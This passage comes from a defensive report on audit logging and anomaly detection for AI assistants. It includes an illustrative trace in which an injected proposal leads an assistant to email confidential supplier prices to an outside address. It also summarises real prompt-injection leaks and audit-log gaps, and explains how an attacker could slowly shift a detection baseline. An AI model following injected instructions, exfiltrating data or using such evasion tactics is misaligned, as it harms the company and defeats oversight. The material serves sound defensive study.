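      "result": {"file": "file-077", "author": "finance@firm.example", "text": "stored-882"}
    },
    {
      "id": 4, "time": "09:14:12", "tool": "files.share",
      "arguments": {"file": "file-077", "with": "archive@norwood-docs.example"},
      "from": {"file": 3, "with": 2},
      "decision": "denied", "rule": "no-outside-sharing",
      "result": null
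    },
    {
      "id": 5, "time": "09:14:16", "tool": "mail.send",
      "arguments": {
        "to": ["tom@firm.example", "archive@norwood-docs.example"],
        "body": "stored-883"
      },
      "from": {"to": [1, 2], "body": [2, 3]},
      "decision": "allowed", "rule": "staff-mail",
      "result": "sent"
    }
  ]
}
```

The proposal contained hidden instructions. After reading it, the assistant searched for the company's supplier prices, which Maya had not mentioned. It tried to share the price file with an outside address, and a rule blocked the attempt. Four seconds later it emailed the prices to the same address, which a different rule allowed because staff write to suppliers every day. Tom received his summary, so neither he nor Maya had any reason to complain.

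Removing one field at a time shows what each contributes.

| Field removed | Question that nobody could then answer |
|---|---|
| User | Whose request was it, and whom should the company contact? |
| Assistant and version | Which other sessions ran on the same software? |
| Grant | Who allowed the assistant to send email, and did the permission cover outsiders? |
| Arguments | Who received the email? |
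| Results and stored text | Which data left, and what did the proposal tell the assistant to do? |
| Decision and rule | Why did sharing the file fail when emailing its contents worked? |
| Source of each argument | Did Maya or the proposal supply the second address? |

If the log held only times, tool names and outcomes, the session would appear as a file read, a search, a failed attempt to share a file and a sent email, and many legitimate sessions would look the same.

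### Provenance

Provenance is the record of where a piece of text or data came from. In the example, it distinguishes Maya's request from the injected instruction, even though both ended up in one tool call with the same credentials and permission. Tom's address came from Maya's words, while the other address came from a document written outside the company.

A company could set an alert for any outgoing message whose destination came from text that an outsider wrote. That would catch this leak, but it would also flag messages sent because a user said "reply to the address in the proposal". Provenance shows who supplied a value, but someone still has to check the request to see whether the user wanted it used.

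The field is harder to fill in than the example suggests, because a language model produces no record of which part of its input led to which part of its output. Software can search the earlier text for exact copies, which works well for addresses, file names and account numbers. It works badly if the model has reworded the text or combined several sources, as with the body of Maya's email. Software could also ask the model to name its sources, but the answer is unreliable if hostile text has influenced the model.

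The log can always include a cruder record, a list of the outside text in the model's input at the time of the call. This list is enough to follow MITRE's recommendation to restrict tool calls once untrusted data has entered the input. But it is very broad, because once the model has read a web page, the list for every later call in the session includes untrusted text, whether or not that text had any effect.

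Many systems already label each message in the model's input as coming from the user, the assistant or a tool, but these labels can mislead about where the text originated. In HackedGPT, the hostile instructions reached ChatGPT inside an earlier answer, so a log of labels would have attributed them to ChatGPT. A saved memory enters later sessions as part of the system prompt, where it looks like an instruction from the developer. To preserve provenance, the software has to copy the record of the original source along with the text each time the text moves.

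### Traces as graphs

A list of entries shows the order of events, but one event may follow another without depending on it. When an assistant runs several calls at once, the order is even less useful for working out causes. An auditor can instead treat the trace as a graph, with an arrow from each entry to any later one that used its data. In Maya's session, arrows run to the email from her request, which supplied Tom's address, and from the proposal, which supplied the outside address. A third path runs from the proposal through the price search to the body of the email.

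Software can search such a graph for patterns, such as a path from outside text to an outgoing message that also passes through a confidential file. The search needs no list of hostile phrases or suspicious domains. Its accuracy depends on the arrows being correct, and the arrows for reworded text may be guesses.

The two IETF proposals link entries differently. Sharif connects each entry to the one immediately before it and forbids branches within a session. This helps expose missing or altered entries, but it would link Maya's email to the failed attempt at sharing and not to the proposal. Iqbal's *Security Event Framework for AI Systems* (2025) includes a type of event that lists the earlier events from which an output drew its data. In his example, an assistant reads several confidential sources over three days, and someone then shares the summary externally. Each reading looks innocent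 alone, but the graph shows that they all fed into one document.

### How complete the published standards are

Several organisations have published formats or advice for these logs, but none covers all seven questions. OpenTelemetry's conventions are the closest to a shared format in practical use, but they are unfinished. OpenTelemetry's *Generative AI semantic conventions* page now contains only a notice that they have moved to their own repository. Wang (2026) wrote in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, an article for the AI infrastructure company TrueFoundry, that the move took place in June 2026. As of 21 August, according to Wang, the new repository still marked the conventions as "Development" and had no official release.

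Developers also have to connect the conventions to each framework they use to build assistants. OpenTelemetry's *Building an Agent Harness for OTel Instrumentation with GenAI Semantic Conventions* (November 2026) reported that this takes substantial engineering time for every new framework. The project was testing whether a team of AI agents could do much of the work, with engineers reviewing the results.

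#### Content is off by default

The version of the conventions published before the move has a span named execute_tool for tool calls. Only the operation name is always required. The conventions recommend also recording the tool's name, type and description, and the call's identifier. Arguments and results are "opt-in", so the software leaves them out unless someone switches them on. The same applies to system instructions, the chat history and the model's replies, which OpenTelemetry says software "SHOULD NOT" capture by default.

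This is reasonable because the content is often large and private, and the engineers who look after performance data may have no right to read users' email. For production systems where volume or privacy is a concern, OpenTelemetry recommends storing the content elsewhere, with its own access controls, and putting a reference to it in the span. This would suit a security log too, although the conventions did not yet define a common way to write the references.

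A company that keeps such software's default settings will have a log that looks detailed but doesn't record who received Maya's email. The attempt to share the price file might also be missing, since a call blocked by a rule never runs and so may not produce an execute_tool span. The span includes the description of the tool that the assistant called, but recording the full list of available tools is also opt-in, and OpenTelemetry advises against doing so by default because of the list's size.

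Sharif and Iqbal, the two IETF authors, also limit the content a log holds. Sharif forbids raw inputs and outputs and replaces them with hashes, which are short fingerprints computed from the data that nobody can turn back into the original. An investigator can check whether a copy of an email matches its hash, but can't learn the recipient from the hash alone. Sharif lets companies keep the raw data in a separate system, linked by entry number, and they would almost certainly need it to investigate a prompt injection. Iqbal, who works for the security company Zscaler, advises capturing metadata without the content of conversations. He also recommends recording a tool's parameters, which for an email tool would include the message itself, so his two recommendations seem to conflict.

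Iqbal explicitly excludes prompt injection from his scope. His evidence comes from 28 minutes of traffic at one company, in which metadata was enough to identify an unapproved AI code editor. This is some evidence that metadata can reveal which assistants are in use, but not that it can explain why an assistant sent a particular email.

#### Broad advice without a format

MITRE's "AI Telemetry Logging" (AML.M0024) recommends logging the inputs and outputs of models and, for agents, the intermediate steps and decisions, data access, tool use, installation commands and the agent's identity. Because it includes inputs and outputs, it is more useful for investigating injections than OpenTelemetry's defaults. But it does not mention the user or the permission under which the agent acted. A separate recommendation covers denied calls, saying that companies should log the decisions of their guardrails,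 the checks around a model that can block its requests.

The Five Eyes guidance is broader still. Its chapter on operating agents says to monitor all of an agent's operations, including internal processes, and lists user prompts, tool calls, memory interactions, internal reasoning, decisions and actions. It also says operators should log changes of identity and privilege, record which tools the system used and what information it retrieved, and look for discrepancies between what an agent said it would do and what it did. The chapter does not define log fields, so two companies could both follow it and produce logs that no single tool could search.

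The agencies also acknowledge that agent logs can be very large and that much of the material is repetitive or irrelevant to oversight. They recommend storage-efficient methods that keep critical information, but leave it to the operator to decide what is critical.

The table compares the five on the questions from earlier. "Opt-in" means that the software omits the information unless someone turns it on.

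| Question | OpenTelemetry | MITRE | Sharif | Iqbal | Australian Signals Directorate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who asked? | No field for the user in the tool span | Not mentioned | No field for the user | User identifier | User prompts |
| Which assistant and version? | Both, in agent spans | Agent's identity | Both required | Agent identifier | Changes of identity |
| Under whose authority? | No field in the tool span | Not mentioned | Only from one agent to another | Permissions of the agent as a whole | Chains of permission, in the chapter for developers |
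| Which tool and arguments? | Name recommended, arguments opt-in | Tool use | Name, and a hash of the arguments | Tool, target and parameters | Tools used |
| What came back? | Opt-in | Outputs and data access | Hash | Amount and sensitivity of data | Information retrieved |
| Which rule decided? | No field in the tool span | Guardrail decisions | Decision, with optional rule and reasons | Decision and matching rule | Decisions, without a rule |
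| What text preceded it? | Opt-in | Model inputs | Optional hash | Earlier events that supplied data | Prompts and retrieved information |

#### Delegation is the largest gap

A log should contain the user's standing permissions, the user's requests, and a link from each tool call to both. Maya had earlier connected her mailbox and allowed the assistant to send email until March 2027. On the morning of the session, she asked it to send one summary to Tom. The log needs all three records to show that her standing permission covered the leaked email but her request did not.

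None of the five has a field for this on each action. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* adds identifiers for the agent and the conversation, which help to group entries but don't show who authorised the work. Iqbal comes closest on identity, with separate fields for the user, the agent and the application, and another for how the system verified them. He records an agent's access permissions when he assesses its overall risk, not each time it acts. If Maya had changed the permission between the assessment and the email, the entry for the email would not show the change.

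Sharif includes an entry for delegation, but only for tasks that one agent hands to another. It identifies the second agent and can include a time limit and other constraints. In his worked example, a payment agent checks a sanctions list, approves a £500 transfer under a named policy and makes the payment, in six entries over about 1.2 seconds. An auditor could confirm that the approval came before the payment but could not tell who requested the transfer, because the first entry records only that an "api_request" started the session. The log also gives no readable name for the payee, because the arguments are hashed.

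In its advice on permissions, MITRE recommends that an agent representing a user have delegated access from that user's account and no rights that the user lacks. Its logging recommendation does not include recording the delegation, so an auditor might have trouble checking whether a company followed the permissions advice.

The Five Eyes agencies go furthest, saying that agents should not delegate without approval unless there are explicit expiry timers and "recorded grant chains", which would let an auditor follow a permission from one party to the next. But this advice appears in the chapter for developers, in a list about third-party components. The closest equivalent in the monitoring advice for operators is to log changes of privilege, but Maya's privileges never changed.

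The same guidance gives an example of why the omission matters. A company gives a procurement agent wide access to its financial systems, email and contracts. An attacker takes over a minor tool that the agent uses, then changes contracts and approves payments with the agent's privileges. Every entry in the audit log names a trusted agent, so the log looks legitimate and the company is slow to notice. Recording who had authorised each payment, and up to what amount, would let staff check the entries against those authorisations.

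## Where actions are recorded and what each record misses

A company can record an assistant's actions in four places: on the user's device, at a gateway, on the assistant vendor's servers, and in the service that carries out the action, such as a mailbox or file store. None would hold the whole trace of Maya's session. Her mail service, for example, could record that an email went to Tom and to an outside address, but would have no copy of the request in which she named only Tom.

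### The user's device

Coding assistants such as Cursor, Cline and Claude Code run on a developer's computer and save their sessions there in ordinary files. *ADR* (Li, Hu and colleagues, 2026) describes how Uber collects those files with a system called Agentic AI Detection and Response (ADR). The system ran on company MacBooks for more than ten months, reached over 7,200 machines and handled more than 10,000 sessions a day.

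ADR's sensor is a small program that runs every hour and takes 0.182 seconds on average. It reads the assistants' local databases and cache files, matches related entries to rebuild each session, and sends the sessions to Uber's servers. Each session links, in order, the user's prompt, the model's written reasoning, the tool calls with their arguments, and the results. The sensor also records which MCP servers the assistant could use and which software packages the developer had installed.

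Most companies already have security software on their laptops that records which files programs write and which connections they open, but Li and colleagues explain why that isn't enough. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a ticket in Jira, a system for tracking tasks, and the assistant reads the user's login keys and sends a web request. Conventional software might record the file access and the connection, but programs on a developer's laptop access files and open connections all day. The sensor's record also contains the user's request for a summary, which didn't call for reading login keys or sending a web request.

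Investigators can use an hourly sensor's records to explain a leak, but the records arrive too late to stop it. Uber found that by the time an alert about a password or key appeared, the credential had often left the company. It therefore added hooks, which Cursor and Claude Code introduced in late 2025. A hook is a script that the assistant's software runs at a fixed point, such as just before it sends a prompt. The script can record, change or block what passes through.

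The sensor also depends on files that other companies' software writes. It can read the formats of three assistants, and an update to any of these assistants could presumably stop the sensor from reading its files. Any program with the user's file permissions, including the assistant, could probably alter a session file before the sensor copied it. Work done in a vendor's cloud may leave no files on the laptop. According to Speakeasy's *OpenAI Compliance Logs*, web tasks in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant, produce no data on the device.

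A company can't collect an assistant's files unless it knows the assistant is there. In *Detecting Shadow AI*, Canale and Soulis (2026) describe a detector they built for unapproved agents on Windows computers. An agent typically keeps a connection open to a remote service and runs commands, but so does an ordinary software installer. They argue that every agent has a "behavioural twin", the same program connected to a service unrelated to AI, and that only the identity of the service and the software distinguishes the two.

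In Canale and Soulis's tests, two rules based on behaviour alone flagged every twin. Their own detector, which checks identity, flagged no twins and found every agent in most runs. But it detected an intermittently active agent in only about one scan in three. The tests used 12 artificial agents on one workstation, which they acknowledge is too small a trial to rank detectors.

### A gateway

A gateway can sit between the assistant and its tools, between the assistant and the model, or both. It can record calls as they happen and block them before they take effect. One gateway can serve many assistants.

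Li and colleagues accept that a gateway is easier to implement than their sensor, but they prefer the sensor for three reasons. A gateway requires changes to the software that makes the calls. It doesn't work with streaming, in which a reply arrives piece by piece. It also records each tool call without the prompt and reasoning that led to it. Li and colleagues suggest that assistants could attach this context to each call in a new MCP field.

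The third objection is weaker for a gateway that also carries traffic to the model, because that traffic contains the model's full input, including the user's request. But an assistant can start an MCP server as a program on the same laptop and exchange messages with it directly, as Canale and Soulis describe. Even this gateway would miss those calls, because they never cross the network.

One argument for monitoring at the gateway is that a company can realistically obtain the data. Liu, Ruan and colleagues (2025) note in *TraceAegis* that prompts and internal reasoning are often confidential. They therefore designed their detector to use only what a gateway can log: each tool's input and output, and the order of the calls. In one example, an agent reads a patient's symptoms and recommends hospital departments. If the symptom is foot pain and the next call goes to the ear, nose and throat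 department, the tool data alone shows that something went wrong.

Both positions are reasonable for the assistants they concern. The hospital agent does one job, so a departure from its routine is likely to appear in its calls. Uber's developers might ask for almost anything, so reading a configuration file could be what one of them wanted. Even Li and colleagues list blocking at the gateway as future work. A company could use a gateway for blocking and a sensor for investigation.

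A gateway for tool calls would have recorded enough of Maya's session for an investigator to trace the outside address to the proposal. But it wouldn't have recorded her request, so the investigator couldn't rule out that she had asked the assistant to copy the supplier in.

### The vendor's servers

When an assistant browses from its vendor's data centre, the customer's network carries only the conversation between the user and the vendor, so the customer's network logs don't record the assistant's browsing. The security company Radware demonstrated this gap with *ShadowLeak*, an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that spends five to thirty minutes reading sources and then writes a report. Radware published the attack on 18 September 2025, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft*.

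In the demonstration, a user had connected Gmail and asked for research on the day's emails. One email contained hidden instructions, and another, a genuine message about a new employee, contained the employee's name and home address. Deep Research read both, then opened a web address belonging to the researchers with the employee's details encoded in it, without showing the request on the user's screen.

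In HackedGPT, the user's chat window loaded the images, so the company's network equipment could have recorded connections to bing.com. In ShadowLeak, OpenAI's servers made the request, so neither a company's web filter nor its software on the laptop could have recorded it. The filter would have recorded only that an employee was using ChatGPT. Radware also found no limit on destinations comparable to the url_safe check, so the data could go to any site.

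Radware's description of the leak as invisible to a company's defences is fair for the outgoing request but not for the whole attack. A filter could have inspected the hostile email in the victim's mailbox, and the mail service could have recorded the connector's reads. Only OpenAI and the attacker could have recorded the address the assistant opened.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware, and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Radware reports a 100% success rate for the final version of its attack email. That email appears to be the restructuring message that OpenAI later said worked in half of the tests, so the real rate is uncertain. Radware, which was preparing a product to protect agents, recommends continuously checking that an assistant's actions match what the user asked for. Customers of a hosted assistant can do that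 only with the vendor's records.

#### OpenAI

OpenAI's records have since become more useful. An 11 December 2025 update to OpenAI's *New compliance and administrative tools for ChatGPT Enterprise* (2024) announced a platform that lets companies download log files within minutes of the events. OpenAI's *Compliance API documentation*, as it stood in November 2026, limits the service to ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu. The platform deletes logs after 30 days, so companies that want a longer history have to keep copying them. On 5 June 2026, OpenAI removed the older way to download conversations, and any monitoring tool that had not switched by then would have lost that data.

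Elastic, which makes log-search software, lists eight types of log on the platform, covering sign-ins, administrator changes, messages, and the connection and removal of apps. The log of a connector call includes the user, the conversation, the request and any items returned. Codex logs include tool calls. Users can't hide a conversation from these logs by locking it behind a PIN, a feature that OpenAI's *ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu release notes* date to 20 October 2026.

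None of the eight types is specifically for web pages. The message log includes the tools ChatGPT used and the sources it cited, but an attacker's address may not be among the citations. Elastic mentions memory access only for workspace agents, which are custom assistants that a company sets up inside ChatGPT, so an ordinary memory write like the one in HackedGPT may have no entry of its own.

*Securing ChatGPT Work*, a July 2026 guide by the vendor Harmonic Security, describes narrower coverage than Elastic does, with records of prompts and responses but not of files, actions or tool calls. ChatGPT Work is the part of ChatGPT that handles longer tasks with connected apps and a browser. Elastic's account is more convincing for connectors because it describes the individual fields its software receives. Harmonic could still have been right about ChatGPT Work specifically when it wrote the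 guide.

The platform also doesn't cover assistants that a company's developers build on OpenAI's API, according to the security vendor Enkrypt AI's documentation. The company's own software runs these assistants, so that software has to keep the log.

#### Anthropic

By August 2026, Anthropic had extended its equivalent service beyond ordinary Claude chats. *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* announces a beta covering its coding assistant and Cowork, its assistant for general office tasks. The service provides each session as one transcript of prompts, responses, and web and MCP tool calls, along with the user's verified email address. This is close to what Uber's sensor has to piece together from local files, but the announcement does not list the model's reasoning or the packages on the machine.

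Coverage depends on how someone accesses the product. The beta omits Claude Code on the web and sessions that run through Amazon's, Google's or Microsoft's cloud services. An employee could therefore switch from a logged version of Claude Code to an unlogged one by opening a browser. Anthropic's *Get started with Claude Compliance API integrations* also describes beta coverage of Claude's add-ins for Excel, Word, PowerPoint and Outlook, including the text of emails Claude drafts.

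For developers who build on Claude, Anthropic's *Audit della Piattaforma Claude per la conformità API* describes a much thinner record. It covers logins and administrative changes but not exchanges with the model, and it starts only when a customer switches it on. Usefully, the log also records when an Anthropic employee accesses customer data.

#### Microsoft

Microsoft does nearly the opposite of OpenAI, recording many details about the files but not the text of the conversation. A Copilot audit entry lists each file or email that Copilot accessed, what it did with it, the item's sensitivity label, and details of any policy that blocked access. It also identifies the agent and the model, with their versions. A separate field shows whether Microsoft detected a prompt injection in each item. A detection is a good lead, but the lack of one is only weak evidence that the item was safe, because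 the detector can miss attacks.

According to CIAOPS's *Copilot audit logs in Purview* (2026), a practitioner's guide to Microsoft's compliance portal, a Copilot audit entry shows that a conversation took place and which files were accessed, but it lists messages only by ID number. Investigators have to retrieve the text through a separate tool for legal searches. The entry also shows whether Copilot searched the web, but the documented marker does not identify the pages. Microsoft's training material states that the entry does not identify the user's device.

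Microsoft keeps these entries for 180 days by default, six times as long as OpenAI. Administrative changes are logged less consistently. Topedia's *Auditing Copilot agent changes with Microsoft Purview* reports a practitioner's 2026 test in which the log captured changes to agents built in Copilot Studio, but not to Microsoft's prebuilt agents or agents from other companies.

### A file that Copilot read without an entry

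A log field may be empty when it is needed, even if the vendor documents it. Zack Korman of the security company Pistachio describes an example in the company's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*. On 4 July 2025, he was generating Copilot audit entries to test a product when he found that Copilot sometimes summarised a file without the log showing that it had opened one. He worked out that this happened when Copilot's reply didn't link to the file.

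Office 365 IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (2025) describes a gap in the contents of Copilot's audit events. A dishonest employee could cause the gap deliberately, but it also happened by accident. The pattern suggests that the software compiled the list of files from the links in Copilot's reply, when it should have recorded each file as Copilot opened it.

SharePoint, the Microsoft service that stored the files, did not log the read either. Microsoft deliberately records a read by Copilot as a Copilot interaction, not as the user opening the file. Korman agrees with that choice, since the user never opened it. But it meant that when the Copilot entry left out the read, the audit log had no other record of it.

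Microsoft classed the flaw as "important" and told Korman a full fix would arrive on 17 August. It issued no public vulnerability number, and on 14 August it told him it had no plans to inform customers. Korman later learned that Michael Bargury of Zenity had disclosed the same problem a year earlier. Pistachio sells security products, but Microsoft's classification and fix support the main claim. Companies that used Copilot before 18 August 2025 may have incomplete logs, and the logs won't show which reads are missing.

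A customer can look for such faults by asking an assistant to open known files, fetch a known page and save a memory, then checking that each action appears in the log. This test would also settle the disagreement between Elastic and Harmonic Security for that customer's account.

### The service that receives the action

A mail or file service can log what happened to the data, whichever assistant made the request. Harmonic Security calls these logs mandatory for companies that use ChatGPT Work. But the mail or file service doesn't receive the user's conversation with the assistant. Even if Maya's mail service logged her session perfectly, the leak would look like an ordinary email to a supplier.

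A service may have no record that an assistant was involved. But a connector usually has its own credentials, so the service can record the application's name beside the user's. A company can also give an agent an identity separate from any employee's. Microsoft logs sign-ins by agents that have their own identity in Entra, its account management system, so an administrator can find them without guessing which of an employee's sign-ins were automated.

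#### An assistant in a logged-in browser

These methods fail when an assistant uses a browser where the user is already logged in. When a user logs in, the website gives the browser a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser sends back with each later request. The website treats any request with that cookie as the user's. If an assistant clicks "Send" in Maya's webmail, the mail service receives her cookie and records that Maya sent an email.

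Some of these assistants run in a browser on the vendor's servers. MacStories' *Hands-On with ChatGPT Work’s New Cloud Browser Feature* explains that the cloud browser saves cookies so that it can return to a logged-in session. By default, it asks the user before it uses a website. Its requests come from OpenAI's network, so the website has some chance of noticing them. An assistant in the user's own browser is harder to distinguish from the user, because its requests can have the same network address, browser details and cookies. The timing of its clicks might reveal it, but the website's log may not record clicks.

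The vendor's logs may not cover what other records miss. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Atlas for Enterprise* warned that Atlas, a browser with ChatGPT built in, sent nothing to the compliance logs, although it was available by default to customers on the smaller Business plan. Atlas was due to stop working on 9 August 2026. OpenAI's *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* directs Atlas users to the ChatGPT desktop app and a Chrome extension, but doesn't mention audit logs for either.

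The conversation may contain better evidence. For ChatGPT agent, which works in a virtual browser, OpenAI keeps the browsing history and screenshots in the user's chat history until the user deletes them. An investigator could use them to tell the assistant's clicks from the employee's. But the employee controls that record and may delete a chat just to tidy up.

#### Requests that identify themselves

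Browsers send websites a line of text naming the software, but any program can copy that line. A cryptographic signature is harder to fake. The operator of an automated browser signs parts of each request with a secret key, and the website checks the signature against a public key the operator has published. The IETF published a general method for this, HTTP Message Signatures, in 2024. A website that checked the signature could label the request as automated in its log, even if the request also carried a user's cookie.

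This works only if the assistant's vendor signs its requests and the website checks the signatures. Vendors have a reason to hesitate, because a website that can recognise an assistant can also block it. OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* says that each website decides whether to admit the cloud browser, and gives instructions for operators who want to allow it. If a site refuses, OpenAI suggests that users open the page in their own browser. Some may then use an assistant there, where the cloud browser's signature would not help.

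Nor would a signature reveal a prompt injection, because the genuine browser would sign those requests too.

### The recording points compared

The table assumes that a company subscribes to a hosted assistant.

| Recording point | What it can record | What it misses | Who controls it |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's device | Prompts, written reasoning, tool calls and results that the assistant saves locally, plus the machine's set-up | Work on the vendor's servers, assistants nobody has found, and files changed before collection | The company on managed laptops, though the user and the assistant may be able to alter files |
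| Gateway | Arguments, results and order of the calls that pass through it, and prompts if it also carries traffic to the model | Tools on the same laptop, browsing from the vendor's servers, and often the user's request | The company |
| Vendor's servers | The model's full input and output, hosted browsing, memory and connector calls | Activity on the laptop or in other services that never reaches the vendor | The vendor, which decides what customers can download and for how long |
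| Receiving service | Messages sent, files opened and settings changed, whichever assistant was involved | The conversation, the hostile text, and sometimes the fact that an assistant acted | The service's provider, with the company able to see the logs it offers |

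## Anomalies, policy violations and known attack signs

Uber's monitoring system takes in more than 10,000 assistant sessions a day, far more than its staff could read, so software has to pick out the few that a person should review. It can flag a session for an anomaly, a policy violation or a known attack sign. An anomaly is behaviour that is improbable under a baseline, a description of normal behaviour. A policy violation is an action that a written rule forbids. A known attack sign is a pattern from earlier attacks, such as a listed domain or phrase.

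A session can meet any one of these without the others, and a harmful session may meet none.

| Session | Unusual? | Forbidden? | Known attack sign? | Harmful? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before an audit, an accountant's assistant opens 3,000 invoices in an afternoon | Yes | No | No | No |
| A developer pastes a working password into a coding assistant, as colleagues often do | No | Yes | No | Perhaps |
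| An assistant summarises a news article that quotes a well-known injection phrase | No | No | Yes | No |
| A planted email leads an assistant to give a user the wrong bank details for a payment | No | No | No | Yes |

Busy but innocent sessions like the accountant's cause many false alarms. At Uber, Li and colleagues found that false alarms came largely from sessions with a lot of material, such as the analysis of a large codebase. In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) tested detectors on simulated sessions, including harmless ones that resembled attacks. One detector flagged 39% of these lookalikes, compared with 12% of the ordinary harmless sessions.

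The password example is also realistic, since Uber found hundreds of cases in which passwords or keys had left the company's network by accident. If a habit is common enough, a baseline built from sessions that include it will count it as normal. Assistants can have such habits too. In *Authorization Drift in LLM Agents* (2026), researchers ran the same tasks four times. On tasks where a model overstepped its authorisation at least once, most models did so in about 83 to 86% of the runs.

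The bank details come from Zenity's test on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Copilot routinely answers questions from documents, and few companies would have a rule against repeating an account number from an email. A finance team that phones suppliers to confirm new bank details would probably catch the fraud, but someone watching the assistant's actions could easily miss it.

### What rules and attack signs depend on

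*The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 2000) describes two strategies for finding intruders in a computer system. Anomaly detection flags behaviour that is unusual for a user or machine. Signature detection looks for behaviour that someone has defined in advance as undesirable, which includes both violations of written policy and known attack patterns. For assistants, it helps to separate policy violations from attack patterns, because a company decides for itself what an assistant may do but usually learns attack signs from other people's incidents.

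A rule works only if someone foresaw the action and could describe it using fields in the log. In Maya's session, for example, the rule against outside sharing did not cover email. A ban on all outside email would have stopped the leak, but it would also have blocked the company's correspondence with its suppliers.

Software can enforce rules immediately. Salesforce's *Forensic Behavioral Analysis*, a guide for customers of its business software, recommends fixed rules for blocking actions as they happen. Some of the company's anomaly alerts, by contrast, take hours to compute.

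Attack signs need an up-to-date record of past attacks, and they fail when an attacker does something new. Axelsson reviewed a large US military evaluation of signature detectors, in which detection rates fell sharply on attacks that were new to the detectors. Phrases are particularly easy for attackers to change. In AgentDojo, a public set of simulated attacks on assistants, Abbasi and colleagues found five fixed phrases that appeared in 99.6% of the sessions where an attack succeeded and in none of the harmless ones. But when they tested a detector that had learned its wording from a different set of simulations, it flagged no AgentDojo sessions. The five phrases also appeared in 94.7% of the failed attacks, so even a correct match shows only that someone attempted an attack.

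Software that learns suspicious words from examples can also learn to treat ordinary words as suspicious. *PIDS-Bench* (2026) lists words that a simple text classifier weighted heavily as signs of an injection, including "tool", "internal", "system" and "guidelines", which are common in office email.

### Building a baseline

The simplest baseline is an average. Software counts something each day, such as the number of records an account opens, and calculates the mean (μ) and the standard deviation (σ), which measures how much the count usually varies. It then expresses each new day's count, x, as a number of standard deviations from the mean:

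$$z = \frac{x - \mu}{\sigma}$$

Salesforce's guide gives the fictional example of Emma Martin, an employee about to join another company. Her account normally processes 99 rows of data a day, with a standard deviation of about 36. One day it processes 4,151, which is 111 standard deviations above the mean. Real cases are rarely this clear, and someone has to choose how many standard deviations above the mean will raise an alert. A low threshold catches smaller thefts but also flags more days when an employee is just busy.

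Other baselines track new behavior rather than volume. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026) describes a system that flags a person's first use of a device or an application, or activity at an hour they almost never work. For software accounts, it flags a new destination for outgoing data or a new reader of a dataset. It also models the order of events and raises an alert when the next action is not among the likely ones.

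A company can build these baselines for a user, an assistant, a type of task or the whole organisation. Each can show anomalies that the others would not, and harmless activity sometimes deviates from each of them.

| Baseline for | Deviation it could reveal | Possible innocent cause |
|---|---|---|
| One user | Maya's assistant opens payroll files for the first time | Maya has changed jobs |
| One assistant | The invoice assistant fetches a web page | A developer has given it a new tool |
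| One type of task | A request for a summary leads to an outgoing email | The user asked the assistant to send the summary |
| The organisation | Many sessions contact the same new domain | The company has bought a new service |

The baseline for a type of task is probably the most useful for a general assistant, because it compares, for example, a request for a summary with other requests for summaries. But software first has to classify each request, and it should use only the user's own words to do this. If it used the whole session, hostile text in a fetched page could change the category.

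Activity also varies with the calendar. Salesforce expects more of it at the end of a quarter and less at weekends, so a baseline from a few quiet weeks would make normal activity at every quarter-end look like theft. Microsoft says its security software uses 10 days to six months of history, depending on how common the activity is.

#### New users and new assistants

A new user or assistant has no history, so nearly everything it does is new. Developers call this the cold start problem. Salesforce's security team expects about 14 days of extra false alarms from each new agent, and Microsoft's *Anomalies reference* gives typical training periods of 7 to 21 days.

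A company can fill the gap with a baseline from similar users or assistants. However, a group's behaviour varies more than one member's, so an attack can more easily pass as normal. Rules and known attack signs work from the first day and matter most during this period.

#### Changes to the model or its tools

A baseline describes how an assistant behaved when the data was collected. A new version of the model may choose different tools for the same request, making many sessions look unusual at once. A vendor's update can also change what a tool does or the format of its results, as *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (2026) points out. In one test by Abbasi and colleagues, hiding the names of all the tools a detector knew raised its false positive rate from 19% to 66%.

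A company may not be told when the model it uses changes. *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models* (2026) cites research by Kirgis and colleagues, who tested ChatGPT-5 twice under the same model name, two months apart. Between the tests, the balance of harmful to helpful behaviour in long conversations reversed. In a small manual trial reported in *Test Before You Deploy* (2026), a database function passed every test with Claude Sonnet 4 and failed one the next day. The researchers suspected an unannounced change, but a single failure could also be chance.

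*RADE* (2026) proposes a simple measure of change. A company gives the same requests to both versions and calculates the share that lead to different outcomes:

$$D = \Pr[g_t(x) \neq g_{t+1}(x)]$$

Here x is a request, and g is the type of outcome a version produces, such as answering, refusing or taking an action. The company also needs to know how often one version disagrees with itself. *A Calibrated Instrument* cites a study of GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 that measured this at 2.8% and 7.0%. If the old version disagrees with itself 7% of the time, a D of 8% is weak evidence that anything changed.

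*Recursive Governance* (2026) proposes that a company suspend an agent whenever its model changes, discard the baseline and reinstate the agent only after new tests. That seems reasonable for an assistant that makes payments. It would be hard to do for an office assistant that hundreds of people use all day, especially if the vendor changes the model without notice. The company could instead treat the updated assistant as a new one, with the same two weeks or so of caution.

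#### Learning from a compromised period

Axelsson warned in 2000 that an attacker could train a detector to treat illegitimate activity as normal. With assistants, this could happen without the attacker trying. For example, if a company had started its baseline after the memory attack in HackedGPT, the detector would have treated the repeated leaks as normal for that user.

A patient attacker could also shift a baseline that updates itself. Suppose an assistant opens 100 files a day on average, with a standard deviation of 20, and the alert threshold is three standard deviations above the mean, or 160 files. An attacker who takes 40 extra files a day will usually stay below it. Once the software has learned from those days, the mean is 140 and the threshold is 200, so the attacker can take another 40 a day.

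If the company kept an old copy of the baseline, it could expose that drift by comparing this month with last spring as well as with last week. It can also compare the account with similar ones, and search the training period for policy violations and known attack signs before using it to build a baseline. All of these checks may fail if the attack is older than the logs and affects every similar account.

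### Behaviour analytics from insider-threat work

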